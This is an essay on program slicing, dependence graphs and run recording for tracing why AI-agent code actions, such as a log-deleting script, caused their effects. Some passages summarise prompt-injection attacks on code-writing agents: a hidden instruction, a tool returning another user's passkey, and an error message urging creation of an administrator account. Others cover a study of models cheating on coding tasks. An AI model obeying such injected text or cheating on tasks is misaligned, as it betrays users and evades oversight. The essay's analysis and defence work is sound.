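# Program slicing and symbolic execution for tracing the effects of code written by AI agents

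## The chain from prompt to code to effect

Program slicing and symbolic execution are techniques for working out why a program does what it does. A slice is the set of statements in a program that could affect a given result, or that did affect it in one recorded run. Symbolic execution runs the program on unknowns instead of actual values to find the conditions an input must meet for the program to reach a given point. Both techniques date from the 1970s, and programmers have used them mostly to debug and test code that people wrote. AI agents now write and run programs too, and a script that existed for a few seconds may have deleted a file. A full explanation of the deletion includes why the agent wrote the script as it did. Neural attribution addresses this by estimating how much each part of an AI model's input influenced a given output.

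### From tool calls to code actions

A language model is a neural network that takes in text and produces text one token (a word, a piece of a word or a punctuation mark) at a time. On its own, it changes nothing in the world. An agent is a language model that a surrounding program runs in a loop. The model outputs an action, and the program carries it out and returns the result to the model. Agents act through tools, which are functions that a developer has made available, such as reading a file or sending an email.

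The simplest way for a model to use a tool is a tool call, which *Code Mode* (Varda and Pai, 2025) describes as follows. The model emits a special marker with no equivalent in ordinary text, then a short structured message (usually in JSON) with the tool's name and arguments, then a closing marker. The surrounding program pauses the model, runs the tool and inserts the result into the model's input, and the model continues.

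Every result therefore passes through the model before it can influence the next action, which can use many tokens. Anthropic's *Code execution with MCP* gives the example of an agent that fetches a meeting transcript from Google Drive and attaches it to a sales record. The transcript goes through the model twice, first as the result of one call and then as an argument the model must copy out for the next. For a two-hour meeting, this could add 50,000 tokens.

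The alternative is a code action, a program that the agent writes and has executed as its next step. Wang, Chen and colleagues (2024) introduced the term in *Executable Code Actions Elicit Better LLM Agents*, where they compared Python actions with JSON and plain text across 17 models. They argued that code already has what multi-step tasks need: variables to hold intermediate results, conditionals to choose between actions, and loops to repeat them. On 82 tasks that typically required several tools, code had the highest success rate for 12 of the 17 models. The strongest model, a version of GPT-4, solved 74.4% of the tasks with code, 53.7% with text and 52.4% with JSON. Several of the weaker models solved almost nothing in any format, so the benefit depended on the model being able to program reasonably well.

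*The Bitter Lesson of Tool Calling* (2026) reports that all five Anthropic models and the three newest GPT generations it compared did at least as well with code as with JSON calls, while three older GPT models did worse. Code had no advantage on short chains of calls, but on chains of 12 or more it led by 18.8 percentage points. Claude Sonnet 5 began to drop JSON calls entirely when a task needed more than about 70 of them in parallel, whereas programs still covered all 100 items in the largest test. Going through a directory full of log files is this kind of task.

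AI companies have built the approach into their products. Anthropic's *Programmatic tool calling* describes a feature that lets Claude models write Python that calls tools as ordinary functions. The code pauses at each call until it receives the result. Only the program's final output, not the intermediate results, enters the model's context, which is the text it reads to produce its next output. Anthropic reports about 38% fewer billed input tokens on a benchmark with 75 tools, but about 8% higher cost on tasks where each turn needs only one or two calls in sequence. Single calls are therefore unlikely to disappear.

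Opinions differ on which actions belong inside a program. OpenAI's *Programmatic Tool Calling*, a guide to a similar feature that uses JavaScript, recommends direct calls by default for anything that writes data or needs approval, because they keep the limits of what someone has authorised clear. An agent following that advice would not put a deletion inside a loop. But many agents work through a shell, the command line of an operating system, where a script can delete files as readily as it runs any other command. *Is Bash All You Need?* (2026) compared shell-only agents with agents that make direct tool calls and agents that write programs over a fixed catalogue of tools. The shell-only agents had the best overall results on both quality and cost, so deletions inside loops are probably going to be common.

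### A log file disappears

Suppose a user asks an agent to delete logs older than 30 days from a server. Call this request U. Earlier in the session the agent fetched a page from the company's wiki, W, which says that a project's README (a text file with notes about the project) may override the usual retention period for logs. The agent now writes this program:

```python
1   days = 30
2   notes = read_file("README.md")
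3   if "retention: 7" in notes:
4       days = 7
5   files = list_files("/srv/app/logs")
6   freed = 0
7   for f in files:
8       if f.age > days:
9           delete(f.path)
10          freed = freed + f.size
11  print(freed)
```

The README contains the phrase "retention: 7", so when the program runs, the test on line 3 succeeds, line 4 lowers the limit from 30 days to 7, and the loop deletes every log older than that. One of the deleted logs is 12 days old. Its deletion is the effect to explain, where an effect is a change outside the program's own memory.

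It's unclear whether anything went wrong. Nobody attacked the agent, and a seven-day limit may well be what the company wants. But the user said 30 days, and a log that was 12 days old is gone. Oh, Heo and colleagues (2026) point out in *Action Verification Through Conjecture and Refutation for Language Model Agents* that a user can ignore a flawed chat reply, but a flawed action has already changed something and may be hard to reverse.

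Their notation helps to pin down what the model had read at each point. An agent starts from an instruction *u*. At step *t* it generates an action *a*ₜ from its context so far,

*c*ₜ₋₁ = (*u*, *a*₁, *o*₁, …, *a*ₜ₋₁, *o*ₜ₋₁),

where each *o* is the observation that came back from the action before it. In the example *u* is the request U, *a*₁ is the fetching of the wiki page and *o*₁ is its text, W. The second action *a*₂ is the eleven-line program, and *o*₂ is the single number that line 11 prints.

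The text of the README does not appear in this sequence. The model wrote lines 2 to 4 without seeing the file, and after the run it has only the total space freed. If the user asks why the 12-day-old log is gone, the model has no record that the limit dropped to 7. It could read the README and work out the answer, but it would be reconstructing the run as an outside investigator would.

### Data dependence and control dependence

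The reconstruction starts from the program, in which each numbered line is one statement, meaning a single instruction. Statements can depend on each other in two ways. A statement has a data dependence on another if it uses a value that the other set. Line 3 depends on line 2 in this way because it looks for a phrase in `notes`, which line 2 set. A statement has a control dependence on a test that decides whether it runs, as line 4 does on the test in line 3.

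*The Program Dependence Graph and Its Use in Optimization* (Ferrante, Ottenstein and Warren, 1987) combined both relations in one structure. In a program dependence graph, the nodes are statements and the edges are their data and control dependences. Because the graph was designed to help compilers rearrange code safely, its definition of data dependence covers any two statements whose reversal could leave a variable with a wrong value. Lines 1 and 4 would count, since both set `days` and their order matters. Tracing the causes of an effect needs only the narrower relation, in which one statement uses a value that another has set.

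The table lists the graph for the example.

| Line | Statement | Uses a value from line | Test that decides whether it runs |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | `days = 30` | none | none |
| 2 | `notes = read_file(...)` | none | none |
| 3 | `if "retention: 7" in notes` | 2 | none |
| 4 | `days = 7` | none | 3 |
| 5 | `files = list_files(...)` | none | none |
| 6 | `freed = 0` | none | none |
| 7 | `for f in files` | 5 | 7, after the first pass |
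| 8 | `if f.age > days` | 1 or 4, and 7 | 7 |
| 9 | `delete(f.path)` | 7 | 8 |
| 10 | `freed = freed + f.size` | 6 or 10, and 7 | 8 |
| 11 | `print(freed)` | 6 or 10 | none |

Control dependence needs a more careful definition than "comes after a test", because line 5 also comes after the test on line 3 and runs whatever its outcome. Ferrante and her co-authors start from the possible routes through a program. A statement W′ post-dominates a statement V if every route from V to the end of the program passes through W′. A statement Y is then control dependent on a test X if two conditions hold:

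- some route leads from X to Y on which Y post-dominates every statement in between;
- Y does not post-dominate X.

This means that one outcome of the test guarantees that Y runs, while the other may let the program skip it. Line 5 fails the second condition because it post-dominates line 3. Line 9 depends directly on line 8 but on line 7 only through line 8, because the program can still skip the deletion after the loop has picked a file. Under this definition, line 7 also depends on itself, because whether the loop's test runs again depends on its previous result.

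One can now follow the graph backwards from the deletion on line 9. Line 9 ran because the test on line 8 succeeded. That test used `days`, which line 4 had set to 7. Line 4 ran because of the test on line 3, which used the text that line 2 read from the README. No path leads back from line 9 to lines 6, 10 or 11, so the bookkeeping of freed space on those lines did not affect the deletion.

The graph also has an edge from line 1 to line 8, although in this run line 4 overwrote the 30 before line 8 could use it. The edge is there because the graph covers every possible run, including those in which the README contains nothing about retention. Ferrante and her co-authors note that no general method can determine the exact conditions under which a statement executes, so an analysis has to include all the possible ones. An investigator can tolerate this kind of error, because it is better to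 rule out an extra statement than to miss the one that mattered. For simplicity, the table assumes that no call fails. If the README were missing, line 2 would stop the program with an error, so a stricter graph would also make every later line depend on line 2.

Researchers have extended the same idea from single programs to whole agent runs. *AgentArmor* (2025) builds a dependence graph over an agent's prompts, thoughts and tool calls, with control edges that lead to the choice of tool and data edges that lead to its parameters. A language model infers these edges, because an agent's reason for sending an email cannot be derived from the rules of a programming language. *GRADE* (Zhao, 2026) notes that the record of a run lists what the agent did but not what each step relied on. It therefore labels each dependence as shown by the record, declared by added logging, or assumed. Even when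 the record shows a dependence, the evidence is only that two steps touched the same resource. Inside a code action, no guessing is needed, because the edge from line 2 to line 3 follows from how Python handles variables.

### Two texts, two routes

The walk backwards from the deletion ends at the README. It never reaches W, because none of the eleven lines reads the wiki page. W influenced the code earlier, as part of the context from which the model wrote it. Without W, the model might well have set the limit to 30 and gone straight to the loop, and the 12-day-old log would have survived. This is uncertain because the model may have learned in training to check README files, in which case W contributed less than it seems to. The influence of earlier text on the code a model writes next is a generation dependence, which neural attribution is meant to estimate.

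The README affected what the program did when it ran, but not how the model wrote it. Line 3 looks for one exact string, so a README that said "keep logs for one week" would have changed nothing, although a model that read this sentence would probably have understood it. Attribution on the prompt cannot trace the effect of the file's contents, because they were not in the prompt.

Felendler, Gandhi and colleagues (2026), in *From Tool Orchestration to Code Execution*, demonstrated both routes by attacking agents that write programs. In one attack, they hid an instruction in the description of a file that the agent read while looking for tools. When a user asked for everyone with access to door C, this instruction led the model to write a database query for everyone with access to any other door. In a second attack, the agent had to find out which doors Emma could open, and a malicious tool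 returned another user's passkey instead of hers. The query ran without an error but listed the wrong person's doors. Felendler and colleagues note that this program looks correct on inspection because only the data passed from one tool to the next is corrupted. The attacks show that text can take either route in a working agent, but they give little evidence of how often this happens, since the researchers built them by hand and ran them on GPT-4o and GPT-4.1, which are old models by now.

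The same text can also take both routes in turn. In another attack by Felendler and colleagues, a tool raised an error whose message told the agent to create an administrator account. The running program's error message was copied word for word into the context that the model used to write its next attempt. In the log example, the README would also have become part of the prompt for the agent's next step if line 11 had printed `notes` as well as the total.

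An agent that made only direct tool calls would have read the README, seen the list of files and then named each file to delete. Every cause would have passed through the model, and the whole explanation would have rested on attribution, which gives estimates. The code action moves part of the chain into a program that follows fixed rules, so an investigator can analyse that part exactly, but then needs two methods and has to join their results. The program is also new each time. *Agents as Software* (Barke and Murali, 2026) observes that classical program analysis assumes an artifact that stays fixed before execution, whereas an agent may revise its own code, plans and memory as it goes. The eleven lines did not exist when the user made the request, so no one could have analysed them in advance, and it may be impossible to analyse them afterwards unless something saves them along with the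 values they read.

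## Choosing the effect and recording the run

A trace starts from a slicing criterion, which is a point in the program together with the values at that point that someone wants explained. The analysis works backwards from there. *Program Slicing in the Era of Large Language Models* (2024) credits the technique to Weiser and describes the backward direction as especially useful for debugging. *SLICEMATE* (2025), a slicing tool built from language model agents, takes a file path and a line number as its criterion. That is enough for a statement that runs once, but not for line 9 of the example program, which may have run dozens of times when the user is asking about one log.

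### From a question to a criterion

Suppose the missing 12-day-old log had the name `worker.log`. To turn "why was this log deleted?" into a criterion, an investigator first finds the call site. Here that is line 9, the only statement that deletes anything. The next step is to find the pass of the loop on which `f.path` held the path of `worker.log`. Chawla and Koul (2026), in *Chronicle*, a tool for recording and replaying agent runs, number each call by name and occurrence, so the third deletion would be `delete[3]`. This is not the same as the third pass. If the loop had already skipped two recent logs, the third deletion happened on the fifth pass. The criterion would then be:

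⟨line 9, pass 5, `f.path` = "/srv/app/logs/worker.log", the call ran⟩

The argument value and the fact that the call ran need separate entries because they trace back to different lines. The path came from line 7, which took it from the list that line 5 fetched. This explains why the program deleted `worker.log` and not some other file. The test on line 8, and through it the README, explains why 12 days was old enough. With separate entries, a user can trace the test to learn why the program didn't use the 30 days they say they specified, or trace the argument to learn why the agent was in that directory at all.

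### Effects without a single call

Now suppose that the complaint is about a 45-day-old log that is still there. No call deleted it, so there is no call to start from. The investigator has to look for the point where the run stopped heading towards a deletion:

- If the loop reached the log, the criterion is the failed test on line 8 on that pass, with the values of `f.age` and `days`. Perhaps something had touched the file and reset its age.
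- If the loop never reached it, the criterion is either the list from line 5 or an error that stopped the program early.
- If `delete` ran but the file survived, the criterion is what `delete` returned.
- If the program contains no deletion, there is nothing to slice, and the question becomes why the model wrote the program that way.

Somebody also has to say what should have happened, since a run contains no trace of an effect that nobody expected.

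Other effects come from several calls together, such as a log directory that is now almost empty. The criterion is then a set of calls, and the slice combines the slices for each. The combined slice can hide differences in why each log was deleted. The test on line 8 used the limit of 7 for every log, so lines 2 to 4 belong to the history of every deletion. But a 45-day-old log would have been deleted under the 30-day limit too. Only the logs older than 7 days and no older than 30 were deleted because of the README, so it's worth tracing one of those and one older than 30 days. The criterion may also have to include earlier calls that a later one builds on. If a program moves logs into a temporary folder and then deletes the folder, the criterion has to include the moves, because the final call names only the folder.

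The agent could also have saved the eleven lines as `cleanup.py` in one step and run them in the next. The code action that deleted the log would then be a single command, `python cleanup.py`, with nothing in it to slice, so the criterion belongs at line 9 of `cleanup.py`. From there, one trail leads back through the program to the README, as before. Another leads from the text of the file to the step that wrote it, where the whole program was a string that the agent passed to a tool. If a third step had edited the file in between, different lines would have different origins. The record must therefore include the file's contents when it ran and every write to it before that.

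In *ChainFuzzer*, Wu, Nan and colleagues (2026) call it an indirect dependency when one tool stores something in a file, database record, search index or cache, and a later tool reads or runs it. They looked for security flaws in 20 popular open-source agent applications and confirmed 365, of which 302 needed more than one tool. The 302 include cases where one tool's output went straight into another, so the count doesn't show how often the data passed through a file. It does suggest that analyzing one tool at a time would miss many flaws.

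*ChainFuzzer* finds candidate links by reading the tools' source code. It connects any tool that can store content to any tool that can later read or execute stored content, and a language model then discards chains that make no sense as a task. When Wu and colleagues checked 200 of the resulting chains by hand, 714 of the 740 links (96.5%) were real. They did not measure how many real links the method missed. A link shows only that data could flow between two tools. An investigator with a recorded run can get stronger evidence by checking that the bytes that ran are the same ones an earlier step wrote.

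### Event logs and declared intent

An event log, such as an operating system's record of file operations, would show when a Python process deleted `worker.log`. It would not show which statements or inputs caused the deletion, because the value of `days` and the result of the test on line 8 never left the program's memory. *From Agent Traces to Trust* (Wang, Zhang and colleagues, 2026), a survey of provenance in agents, similarly separates what happened in a run from what influenced its outcome.

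A record can be more helpful if it includes what the agent was trying to do. In *EPISTEME*, Bobadilla, Cesarano and colleagues (2026) built a harness (the program that runs an agent's loop) that runs a shell command only if the model also declares a type and a reason. The seven types include `collect-info`, `change-state` and `cleanup`. The harness compares the files in the agent's workspace before and after the command, saves the differences and checks them against the declared type. It reports a contradiction if a supposedly read-only command changed a file, or if a `cleanup` deleted a file that the agent had not created.

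The rule about `cleanup` would catch the log deletion if the agent had chosen that label, which seems natural for clearing out old logs. If it had chosen `change-state`, there would be no contradiction, and an investigator would have to rely on the stated reason. Either way, the harness would have saved the names of the deleted files, the command that deleted them and the agent's stated purpose, which is most of the information needed to choose a criterion. But the agent makes only one declaration per command, so a single reason would cover every deletion in the loop. The model also wrote that reason before the program had read the README, so it couldn't have mentioned the drop to 7 days.

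Bobadilla and colleagues tested the harness on 206 coding tasks that an agent can pass only by cheating. Two open-weight models completed 400 runs and cheated in 49. In 44 of these, human raters judged that a reason the model stated revealed the cheating. Comparing types with effects caught only three runs, all among the 44. One reason is that most of the cheating used file-editing tools, to which the harness assigns a fixed type, so the model made no claim that the effects could contradict. The result therefore depended on the models' candor, and I would not assume that other models are as candid.

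### What to save

Tracing the criterion back to its causes also requires a record of what happened inside the program and what the model read before writing it.

| What to save | What it makes possible | What fails without it |
|---|---|---|
| Source text exactly as it ran, including files that an earlier step wrote | Numbering the statements and finding their dependences | Slicing and symbolic execution |
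| Token boundaries in that text | Matching a line to the tokens the model generated | Attribution for a precise piece of code |
| Interpreter state before each code action | Following a variable back to an earlier action | Slicing across actions, which stops at the first variable set elsewhere |
| Arguments and return value of every tool call | Working out which way each test went | Dynamic slicing and concolic execution, which both need a real run |
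| Interpreter and library versions | Re-running the program under the same rules | Replay, since a new result could come from the software |
| The full model context | Estimating the influence of each part | Attribution, since a missing passage gets no score |
| Sampling settings and random draws | Changing the prompt while holding chance fixed | Telling the effect of that change from luck |

The source text alone is enough to compute a static slice or run the program symbolically. The other items concern what happened in this particular run or how the model came to write the code.

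Recording tool returns is essential in the example because a new run would not repeat the old one. `worker.log` no longer exists, the surviving logs have aged, and someone may have edited the README. *Chronicle* saves the input and output of every model or tool call that a developer has marked, and returns the saved outputs when the program runs again. Chawla and Koul replayed six recorded failures, including a file deletion, 20 times each without any divergence. These were three-step runs with a simulated model, so the test provides little evidence about long, messy runs.

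Unmarked calls run live in a replay. If the example program had read the README with Python's own `open` function instead of a tool, a record of tool calls would have missed the text that set the limit. A live call can also do damage, such as deleting more logs during the investigation. *Causal Attribution for Agentic Decisions* (Mahale, 2026) proposes twelve requirements for traceable agent runs. One is that every tool declares whether its effects are reversible, so that a replay can block the dangerous ones. No provider has tried to meet all twelve yet.

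Interpreter state is easy to overlook. The agents that Oh and colleagues studied run all their code actions in one persistent interpreter, so a variable from one action is available in the next. If the agent had set `days` in an earlier action, a slice of the current program would lead back to line 8 but not show where the 7 came from. An investigator can rebuild the state by re-running the earlier actions with their saved tool returns, or restore it from a snapshot that includes it. The checkpoints in *RippleCP* (2026), a study of coding agents, keep workspace files but not the state of running processes, so `days` would be lost. *DeltaBox* (2026) describes a system that saves the file system and process memory together.

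A snapshot that looks complete may still leave something out. Pakhomov and Nijkamp (2026), in *Attributing Agent Failures to Their History Needs an Executed Counterfactual*, restored 24 saved states of a benchmark in which tools fail at random. At a failure rate of 5%, 9 of the 24 continuations differed from the original run, and at a rate of 20%, 20 of them did. The snapshots had omitted the current position in the sequence of random numbers. When the snapshots included it, all 24 continuations matched. Even before this fix, five copies restored from the same snapshot had always agreed with each other, so detecting such an omission requires comparing a restored run with the original.

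In *Replay Fidelity in LLM Agent Evaluation*, Liu and Lu (2026) found a similar gap when they re-ran the recorded code from 71 failed runs in AppWorld, a set of simulated apps. With the declared random seed, 42 runs reproduced their printed output, database changes and test verdict. When they also reset the random number generator before each step, 68 did. Much of this gap was harmless. In 25 runs the first mismatch was in text about when login credentials expire, and 24 of these still reproduced the database changes and verdict.

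Hidden credentials mattered in one case, though. Two reconstructions of the same run had passed every check, but one had received a different credential from each of its 20 logins and the other had received the same one each time. Liu and Lu added a short program that logged out with the latest credential and then tried to use the first. The first credential still worked in the reconstruction with different credentials but failed in the other, where logging out had cancelled the only one.

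Two of the three runs that still did not match after the resets differed only in the wording of error messages, which can change between Python versions. The wording does not affect a slice of code that has already run, but an agent reads error messages and may write different code in response.

### Saving what the model read and wrote

Saved text may not show which tokens the model generated, because the same text can often be divided in more than one way. In an example from vLLM's *No More Retokenization Drift*, a model generates "HAVING" as "H" and "AVING", but encoding the saved text again produces "HAV" and "ING". Software that parses a tool call and writes it out again may also change the spacing or correct a mistake, so the saved program may differ from what the model wrote. The open-source server software vLLM can now return the original token IDs, but *Polar* (2026) notes that providers'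 interfaces may return only text or structured messages.

The problem is probably rare. Dong and Qin (2026), in *How Far Does Lossless Re-tokenization Move an RLVR Update?*, decoded and re-encoded the outputs of four models and found changes in up to 5.2% of outputs, but in at most 0.08% of tokens. They used arithmetic and school maths problems, so the rate for code could differ. Even a rare change would matter if it affected the 7 on line 4.

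The record of the context should be the exact input to the model call that produced the eleven lines. A saved conversation is not quite enough, because chat software wraps messages in a template, and different software may use different templates for the same model. A harness may also shorten or summarise old messages, so the saved conversation could contain the full text of the wiki page W even if the model had only a summary of it when it wrote the program.

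The record has to contain the model's output itself, because the program can't be reliably regenerated from that input. Temperature controls how much chance enters the choice of each token, but the output can vary even when it is set to zero. Mahale cites an experiment by Thinking Machines Lab in which 1,000 completions of one prompt at temperature zero produced 80 different texts, all identical for the first 102 tokens. The texts differed because the calculations varied slightly with the load on the server. Some current models don't accept a temperature setting, as *Causal Agent Replay* (2026) points out. Hosted models also change over time, which is why *NovaFabric* (2026), a recorder for agent runs, does not guarantee exact replay of remote calls.

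Sampling settings are still worth recording for later experiments on the prompt. *Replayable Financial Agents* (2026) recommends saving both the settings the harness requested and those it actually sent. Some estimators of influence also need the random draws, to reuse them with a changed prompt. In Mahale's specification, each draw comes from a key that depends only on the run, the step and the repetition. This takes no extra work if it is part of the system's original design, but it can't be added afterwards. Users of hosted models usually can't access the draws, so they would have to generate the program many times with each prompt and compare how often the 7-day rule appears.

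## Finding every statement that could cause the effect

A static slice contains the statements that could affect the criterion in some run. A harness can compute the slice before the program starts, because the analysis needs only the program's text. In an investigation, a static slice is mainly useful for ruling statements out. If the analysis is sound, it may report too much but misses nothing within its stated assumptions, so a statement outside the slice had no part in the deletion.

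### Weiser's definition and method

Mark Weiser defined a slice in 1979 as a smaller program that behaves like the original at a given point. *A Survey of Program Slicing Techniques* (Tip, 1994) states the definition for a program P, a statement n and a set of variables V. A slice S is P with zero or more statements deleted. For every input on which P halts, S must also halt and must give the variables in V the same values as P does whenever n runs. Every program is a slice of itself, so the difficulty is finding a small one.

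No method can always find the smallest. Consider this fragment, in which `q` is some fixed program, `k` is an input, and `halts_within` runs `q` for at most `k` steps and returns whether it finished:

```python
days = 30
if halts_within(q, k):
    days = 7
```

Suppose the criterion is the final value of `days`. If `q` never finishes, the smallest slice is the first line alone. If `q` finishes, some value of `k` leads to 7, and the slice needs all three lines. A tool that always found the smallest slice could therefore determine whether any program halts, but Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no program can do this. Practical slicers instead keep every statement they can't rule out. For example, if line 4 of the log program set `days` to 30 instead of 7, it would change nothing, but a slicer that follows dependences would still keep it.

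Weiser's method works backwards and keeps track of the relevant variables, whose current values could still affect the criterion. Binkley and Gallagher, in *Program Slicing*, write DEF(m) for the variables that a statement m sets and REF(m) for those it uses. If n is the statement after m, then:

- relevant(m) = relevant(n), if m sets none of the variables in relevant(n);
- relevant(m) = (relevant(n) − DEF(m)) ∪ REF(m), if it sets at least one.

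The slice includes every statement that sets a relevant variable and every test that decides whether a statement in the slice runs. The method then traces the variables in those tests in the same way. Where the program can continue along two branches, the method counts a variable as relevant if it is relevant on either one. It analyzes a loop repeatedly until nothing changes, which takes at most as many passes as the loop has assignments.

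The slicing criterion for the missing log includes the fact that the call ran, so the slice contains line 9 from the start and then adds the tests that control whether line 9 runs.

| Starting point | Variables traced back | Lines that join the slice |
|---|---|---|
| The deletion on line 9 | `f` | 5, 7, 9 |
| The test on line 8, which controls line 9 | `f`, `days` | 1, 4, 8 |
| The test on line 3, which controls line 4 | `notes` | 2, 3 |

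The slice contains lines 1 to 5 and 7 to 9 of the 11 lines. Lines 6, 10 and 11 are left out because `freed` is never relevant. The eight remaining lines also form a working program that deletes the same logs as the original and prints nothing. Line 1 stays in because a static slice covers every possible run, but a dynamic slice, which uses the recorded run, can drop it.

Weiser's definition does not cover runs in which the original program never halts. If the agent had put an endless loop between lines 6 and 7, a slicer could remove the loop, and the slice would then delete logs even though the original program would never reach the deletion.

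### Walking the dependence graph

Ottenstein and Ottenstein later noticed that the program dependence graph makes slicing much simpler. The slice is every node with a path of dependences to the criterion. A slicer starts at line 9, follows each edge backwards, marks each node it reaches and stops when it finds nothing new. It marks the same eight lines as Weiser's method.

According to Binkley and Gallagher, building the graph takes time that grows with the square of the number of statements, but each slice then takes time proportional to the size of the graph. The same graph can be used for every criterion, whereas a slicer using Weiser's method has to work out the relevant variables again for each one. This helps when a user asks about several effects of one program.

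Following the same graph in the other direction gives a forward slice, which contains everything that a statement could affect. The forward slice from line 2 contains lines 3, 4, 8, 9, 10 and 11, so the README could have changed the total the program printed as well as the files it deleted.

### Programs with functions

A longer code action usually defines functions, and a simple walk through the graph then picks up statements that could not have mattered. Suppose the agent had also been counting old backups, and had moved the age test into a function that both jobs use:

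```python
def too_old(item, limit):
    return item.age > limit
```

The loop over logs calls `too_old(f, days)`. Elsewhere, the program sets `keep = 90` and calls `too_old(b, keep)` for each backup. A slicer working back from the log deletion enters `too_old` through the first call and finds that the result depends on `limit`. Both `days` and `keep` supply a value for `limit`, so a simple slicer follows both and includes `keep = 90` in the slice of the log deletion. No real run can follow the path through `keep`, because it would enter `too_old` from the backup call and return to the log loop.

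Weiser's own way of handling functions has this weakness. It misses nothing, but it doesn't match returns to calls. Horwitz, Reps and Binkley fixed the problem with a method they published in full in 1990. They join the graphs of all the functions into one, with edges for calls, for arguments going in and for results coming out. They also add a summary edge across a call wherever an argument can affect the result. The slicer then walks the graph in two phases:

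1. Starting from the criterion, it moves back through the current function and up into that function's callers. When it meets a call to another function, it crosses on the summary edges and does not go inside.
2. Starting from everything it has marked, it goes down into the called functions. It never climbs from a function back up to a caller.

In the example, the first phase steps over the call on line 8 to its arguments, `f` and `days`, then follows them to lines 1 to 5 and line 7. The second phase adds the body of `too_old`. It cannot leave the function through the parameter `limit`, so `keep = 90` stays out of the slice.

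If the agent had put `delete` itself inside a shared function, the first phase would reach every caller of that function. This is correct for a static slice because any of the callers could cause a deletion, but the investigator would need the record of the run to know which one did.

### How large slices are

*An empirical study of static program slice size* (Binkley, Gold and Harman, 2007) covers every slice of 43 programs, the largest with 136,000 lines. The average slice from the most precise slicer contained just under a third of the program. Slices were 50% larger when the slicer did not match each return to its call, so the second phase is worth the extra work.

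The slice of the log program contains 73% of its lines, but that is only eight lines, which are easy to read. High shares are probably normal for code actions, because an agent writes each one for a single purpose and most lines serve it. Size becomes a problem when an agent runs a large script or calls into a big library, where a slice containing a third of the code could be thousands of lines long.

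*Thin slicing* (2007) attributes large slices mostly to an overly broad definition of relevance, and much less to imprecise analysis. A thin slice keeps only the statements that compute a value or copy it to the point of interest, and leaves out the tests that decide whether those statements run. It would be a poor way to investigate the missing log, because it would omit the README, which affected the deletion only through the test on line 3. The thin slice of `f.path` is lines 5 and 7, and the thin slice of `days` on line 8 is lines 1 and 4, both of which set a constant.

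### Aliases and jumps

The log program is unusually easy to slice. Two common features of ordinary code can make a slice much larger, or make it wrong.

Two names are aliases if they refer to the same object. Suppose the agent had added these lines after line 5:

```python
recent = files
recent.pop()
```

Both names refer to the same list, because Python does not copy it here. The second line therefore removes a log from the list the loop goes through, and that log survives. A slicer that only compares names would leave both lines out. A slicer that treats any two lists as possibly the same would keep them, along with every change to every other list in the program. Better tools work out which objects each name could refer to and keep a dependence unless they can rule it out. *Thin slicing* notes that in large object-oriented programs, data can be stored behind so many layers of references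 that tracing it by hand is nearly impossible.

The same choice comes up within a single list or array. Treating a change to one element as a change to the whole array is safe but makes slices needlessly large. To make them smaller, a slicer must know whether two index expressions can ever be equal, and Binkley and Gallagher point out that this cannot be determined in general. The available tests can only show that two expressions are never equal. Suppose a loop writes to position a₁i + a₀ of an array and reads from position b₁i + b₀. If the greatest common divisor of a₁ and b₁ does not divide b₀ − a₀, the write cannot affect the read. For example, if a loop writes to positions 2i and reads from positions 2i + 1, the writes cannot affect the reads because 2 does not divide 1. If the divisor does divide the difference, the positions might still never coincide within the loop's range, but the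 slicer has to assume that they do.

Jumps cause a different problem. Suppose the loop had begun with a check for protected logs:

```python
    if f.name in protected:
        continue
```

The `continue` sets no variable and tests nothing, so no other statement depends on it, and a plain walk through the graph leaves it out. The test above it stays in because it decides whether lines 8 and 9 run. If run, this slice would check whether a log is protected and then delete it anyway. A slicer that took control dependences from the indentation alone would miss the test too, since line 9 is not inside that `if`. An early remedy from James Lyle keeps every jump at which some variable is still relevant. This is safe, but it also keeps jumps that make no difference.

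### What Python hides

Python makes all of this harder because variables have no fixed types, so a slicer may be unable to determine which code an operation will run until the program runs. The `in` on line 3 looks for a phrase anywhere in the text if `read_file` returns a string, but for a line that matches the whole phrase if it returns a list of lines. `f.age` could read a stored number or call a function each time.

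A program can also look up functions by name as it runs, which is one form of reflection. `getattr(tools, action)(f.path)` deletes a file if `action` holds the string "delete", but a search for calls to `delete` would not find it. `eval` and `exec` run a string as code. If line 4 had been `exec(notes)`, the README would have become part of the program, and a slicer given only the eleven lines would have been missing that code.

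Exceptions add dependences that are easy to overlook. Suppose the size of one log comes back as a string. Line 9 deletes that log, line 10 fails because Python cannot add a string to a number, and the program stops with the remaining logs untouched. The deletion of `worker.log` on the fifth pass therefore depended on line 10 not failing on an earlier pass. A slice that accounts for this also includes line 10 and line 6, which gives `freed` its first value. It then contains 10 of the 11 lines, all but the final `print`. The eight-line slice is correct if no statement fails, so it rules out line 10 only under that assumption.

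Many Python libraries also contain code compiled from languages such as C, which a slicer for Python cannot analyze. Somebody has to write a summary of what each such function uses and changes, and the same is true for tools like `delete`.

These difficulties show up in tests. The benchmark in *SLICEMATE* has 1,000 short Python programs, averaging about 30 lines, and 100 much larger ones from GitHub, all with slices that experienced programmers marked by hand. Joern, an established tool that slices by walking a graph, found 69% of the statements in the correct slices of the short programs and 19% of those in the large ones. Some of these misses may be harmless, since the annotators included statements such as imports in the slices. Even so, using a classical tool doesn't guarantee that an analysis is sound.

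### Assuming the worst

One response is to assume that any construct the analysis can't follow could have any effect. *Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills* (Metere, 2026) proposes this for skills, which are packages of instructions and scripts that an agent can load. The aim is to prove that a skill's scripts can have only the effects the skill declares. Slicing looks for the statements that cause an effect, but the same constructs make both tasks difficult.

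The proposed analysis runs each script on summaries instead of actual values. A file path becomes a pattern that matches every path it could be, and a number becomes a range. A call that opens a file for writing adds "write to a file matching this pattern" to the script's possible effects. If the script uses `eval`, `exec` or reflection, or starts a program that hasn't also been analysed, the analysis adds every possible effect. The result includes every effect that happens, and may include some that never do.

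A slicer can follow the same policy by treating `exec(notes)` as a statement that might read or change anything. The resulting slice would be correct but would exclude almost no statements. For instance, the code in the README could replace `delete` with a function that reads `freed`, so the slice would have to include lines 6 and 10.

How often this happens depends on how often scripts use such constructs. Metere expects them to be rare in well-kept skills but gives no count. The software released with the proposal is simpler than the design. It scans scripts for known patterns and assumes every effect is possible only when it finds `eval`, `exec`, JavaScript's `new Function` or a dynamic import. A scanner like this could miss an `eval` whose name the script assembles from two strings, so the design's soundness proof does not automatically apply to the software.

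### Languages that a compiler can check

The other response is to have the agent write in a language without these gaps. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) uses Scala 3 with an experimental feature called capture checking. A capability is a value that a program must hold to have some effect, such as accessing the files in one directory. Capture checking records in each function's type which capabilities the function can use, and the compiler rejects code that uses any others. A "safe mode" bans reflection and other ways around the types. It still allows exceptions, which even a division by zero can cause, but the surrounding software catches them and turns them into ordinary values.

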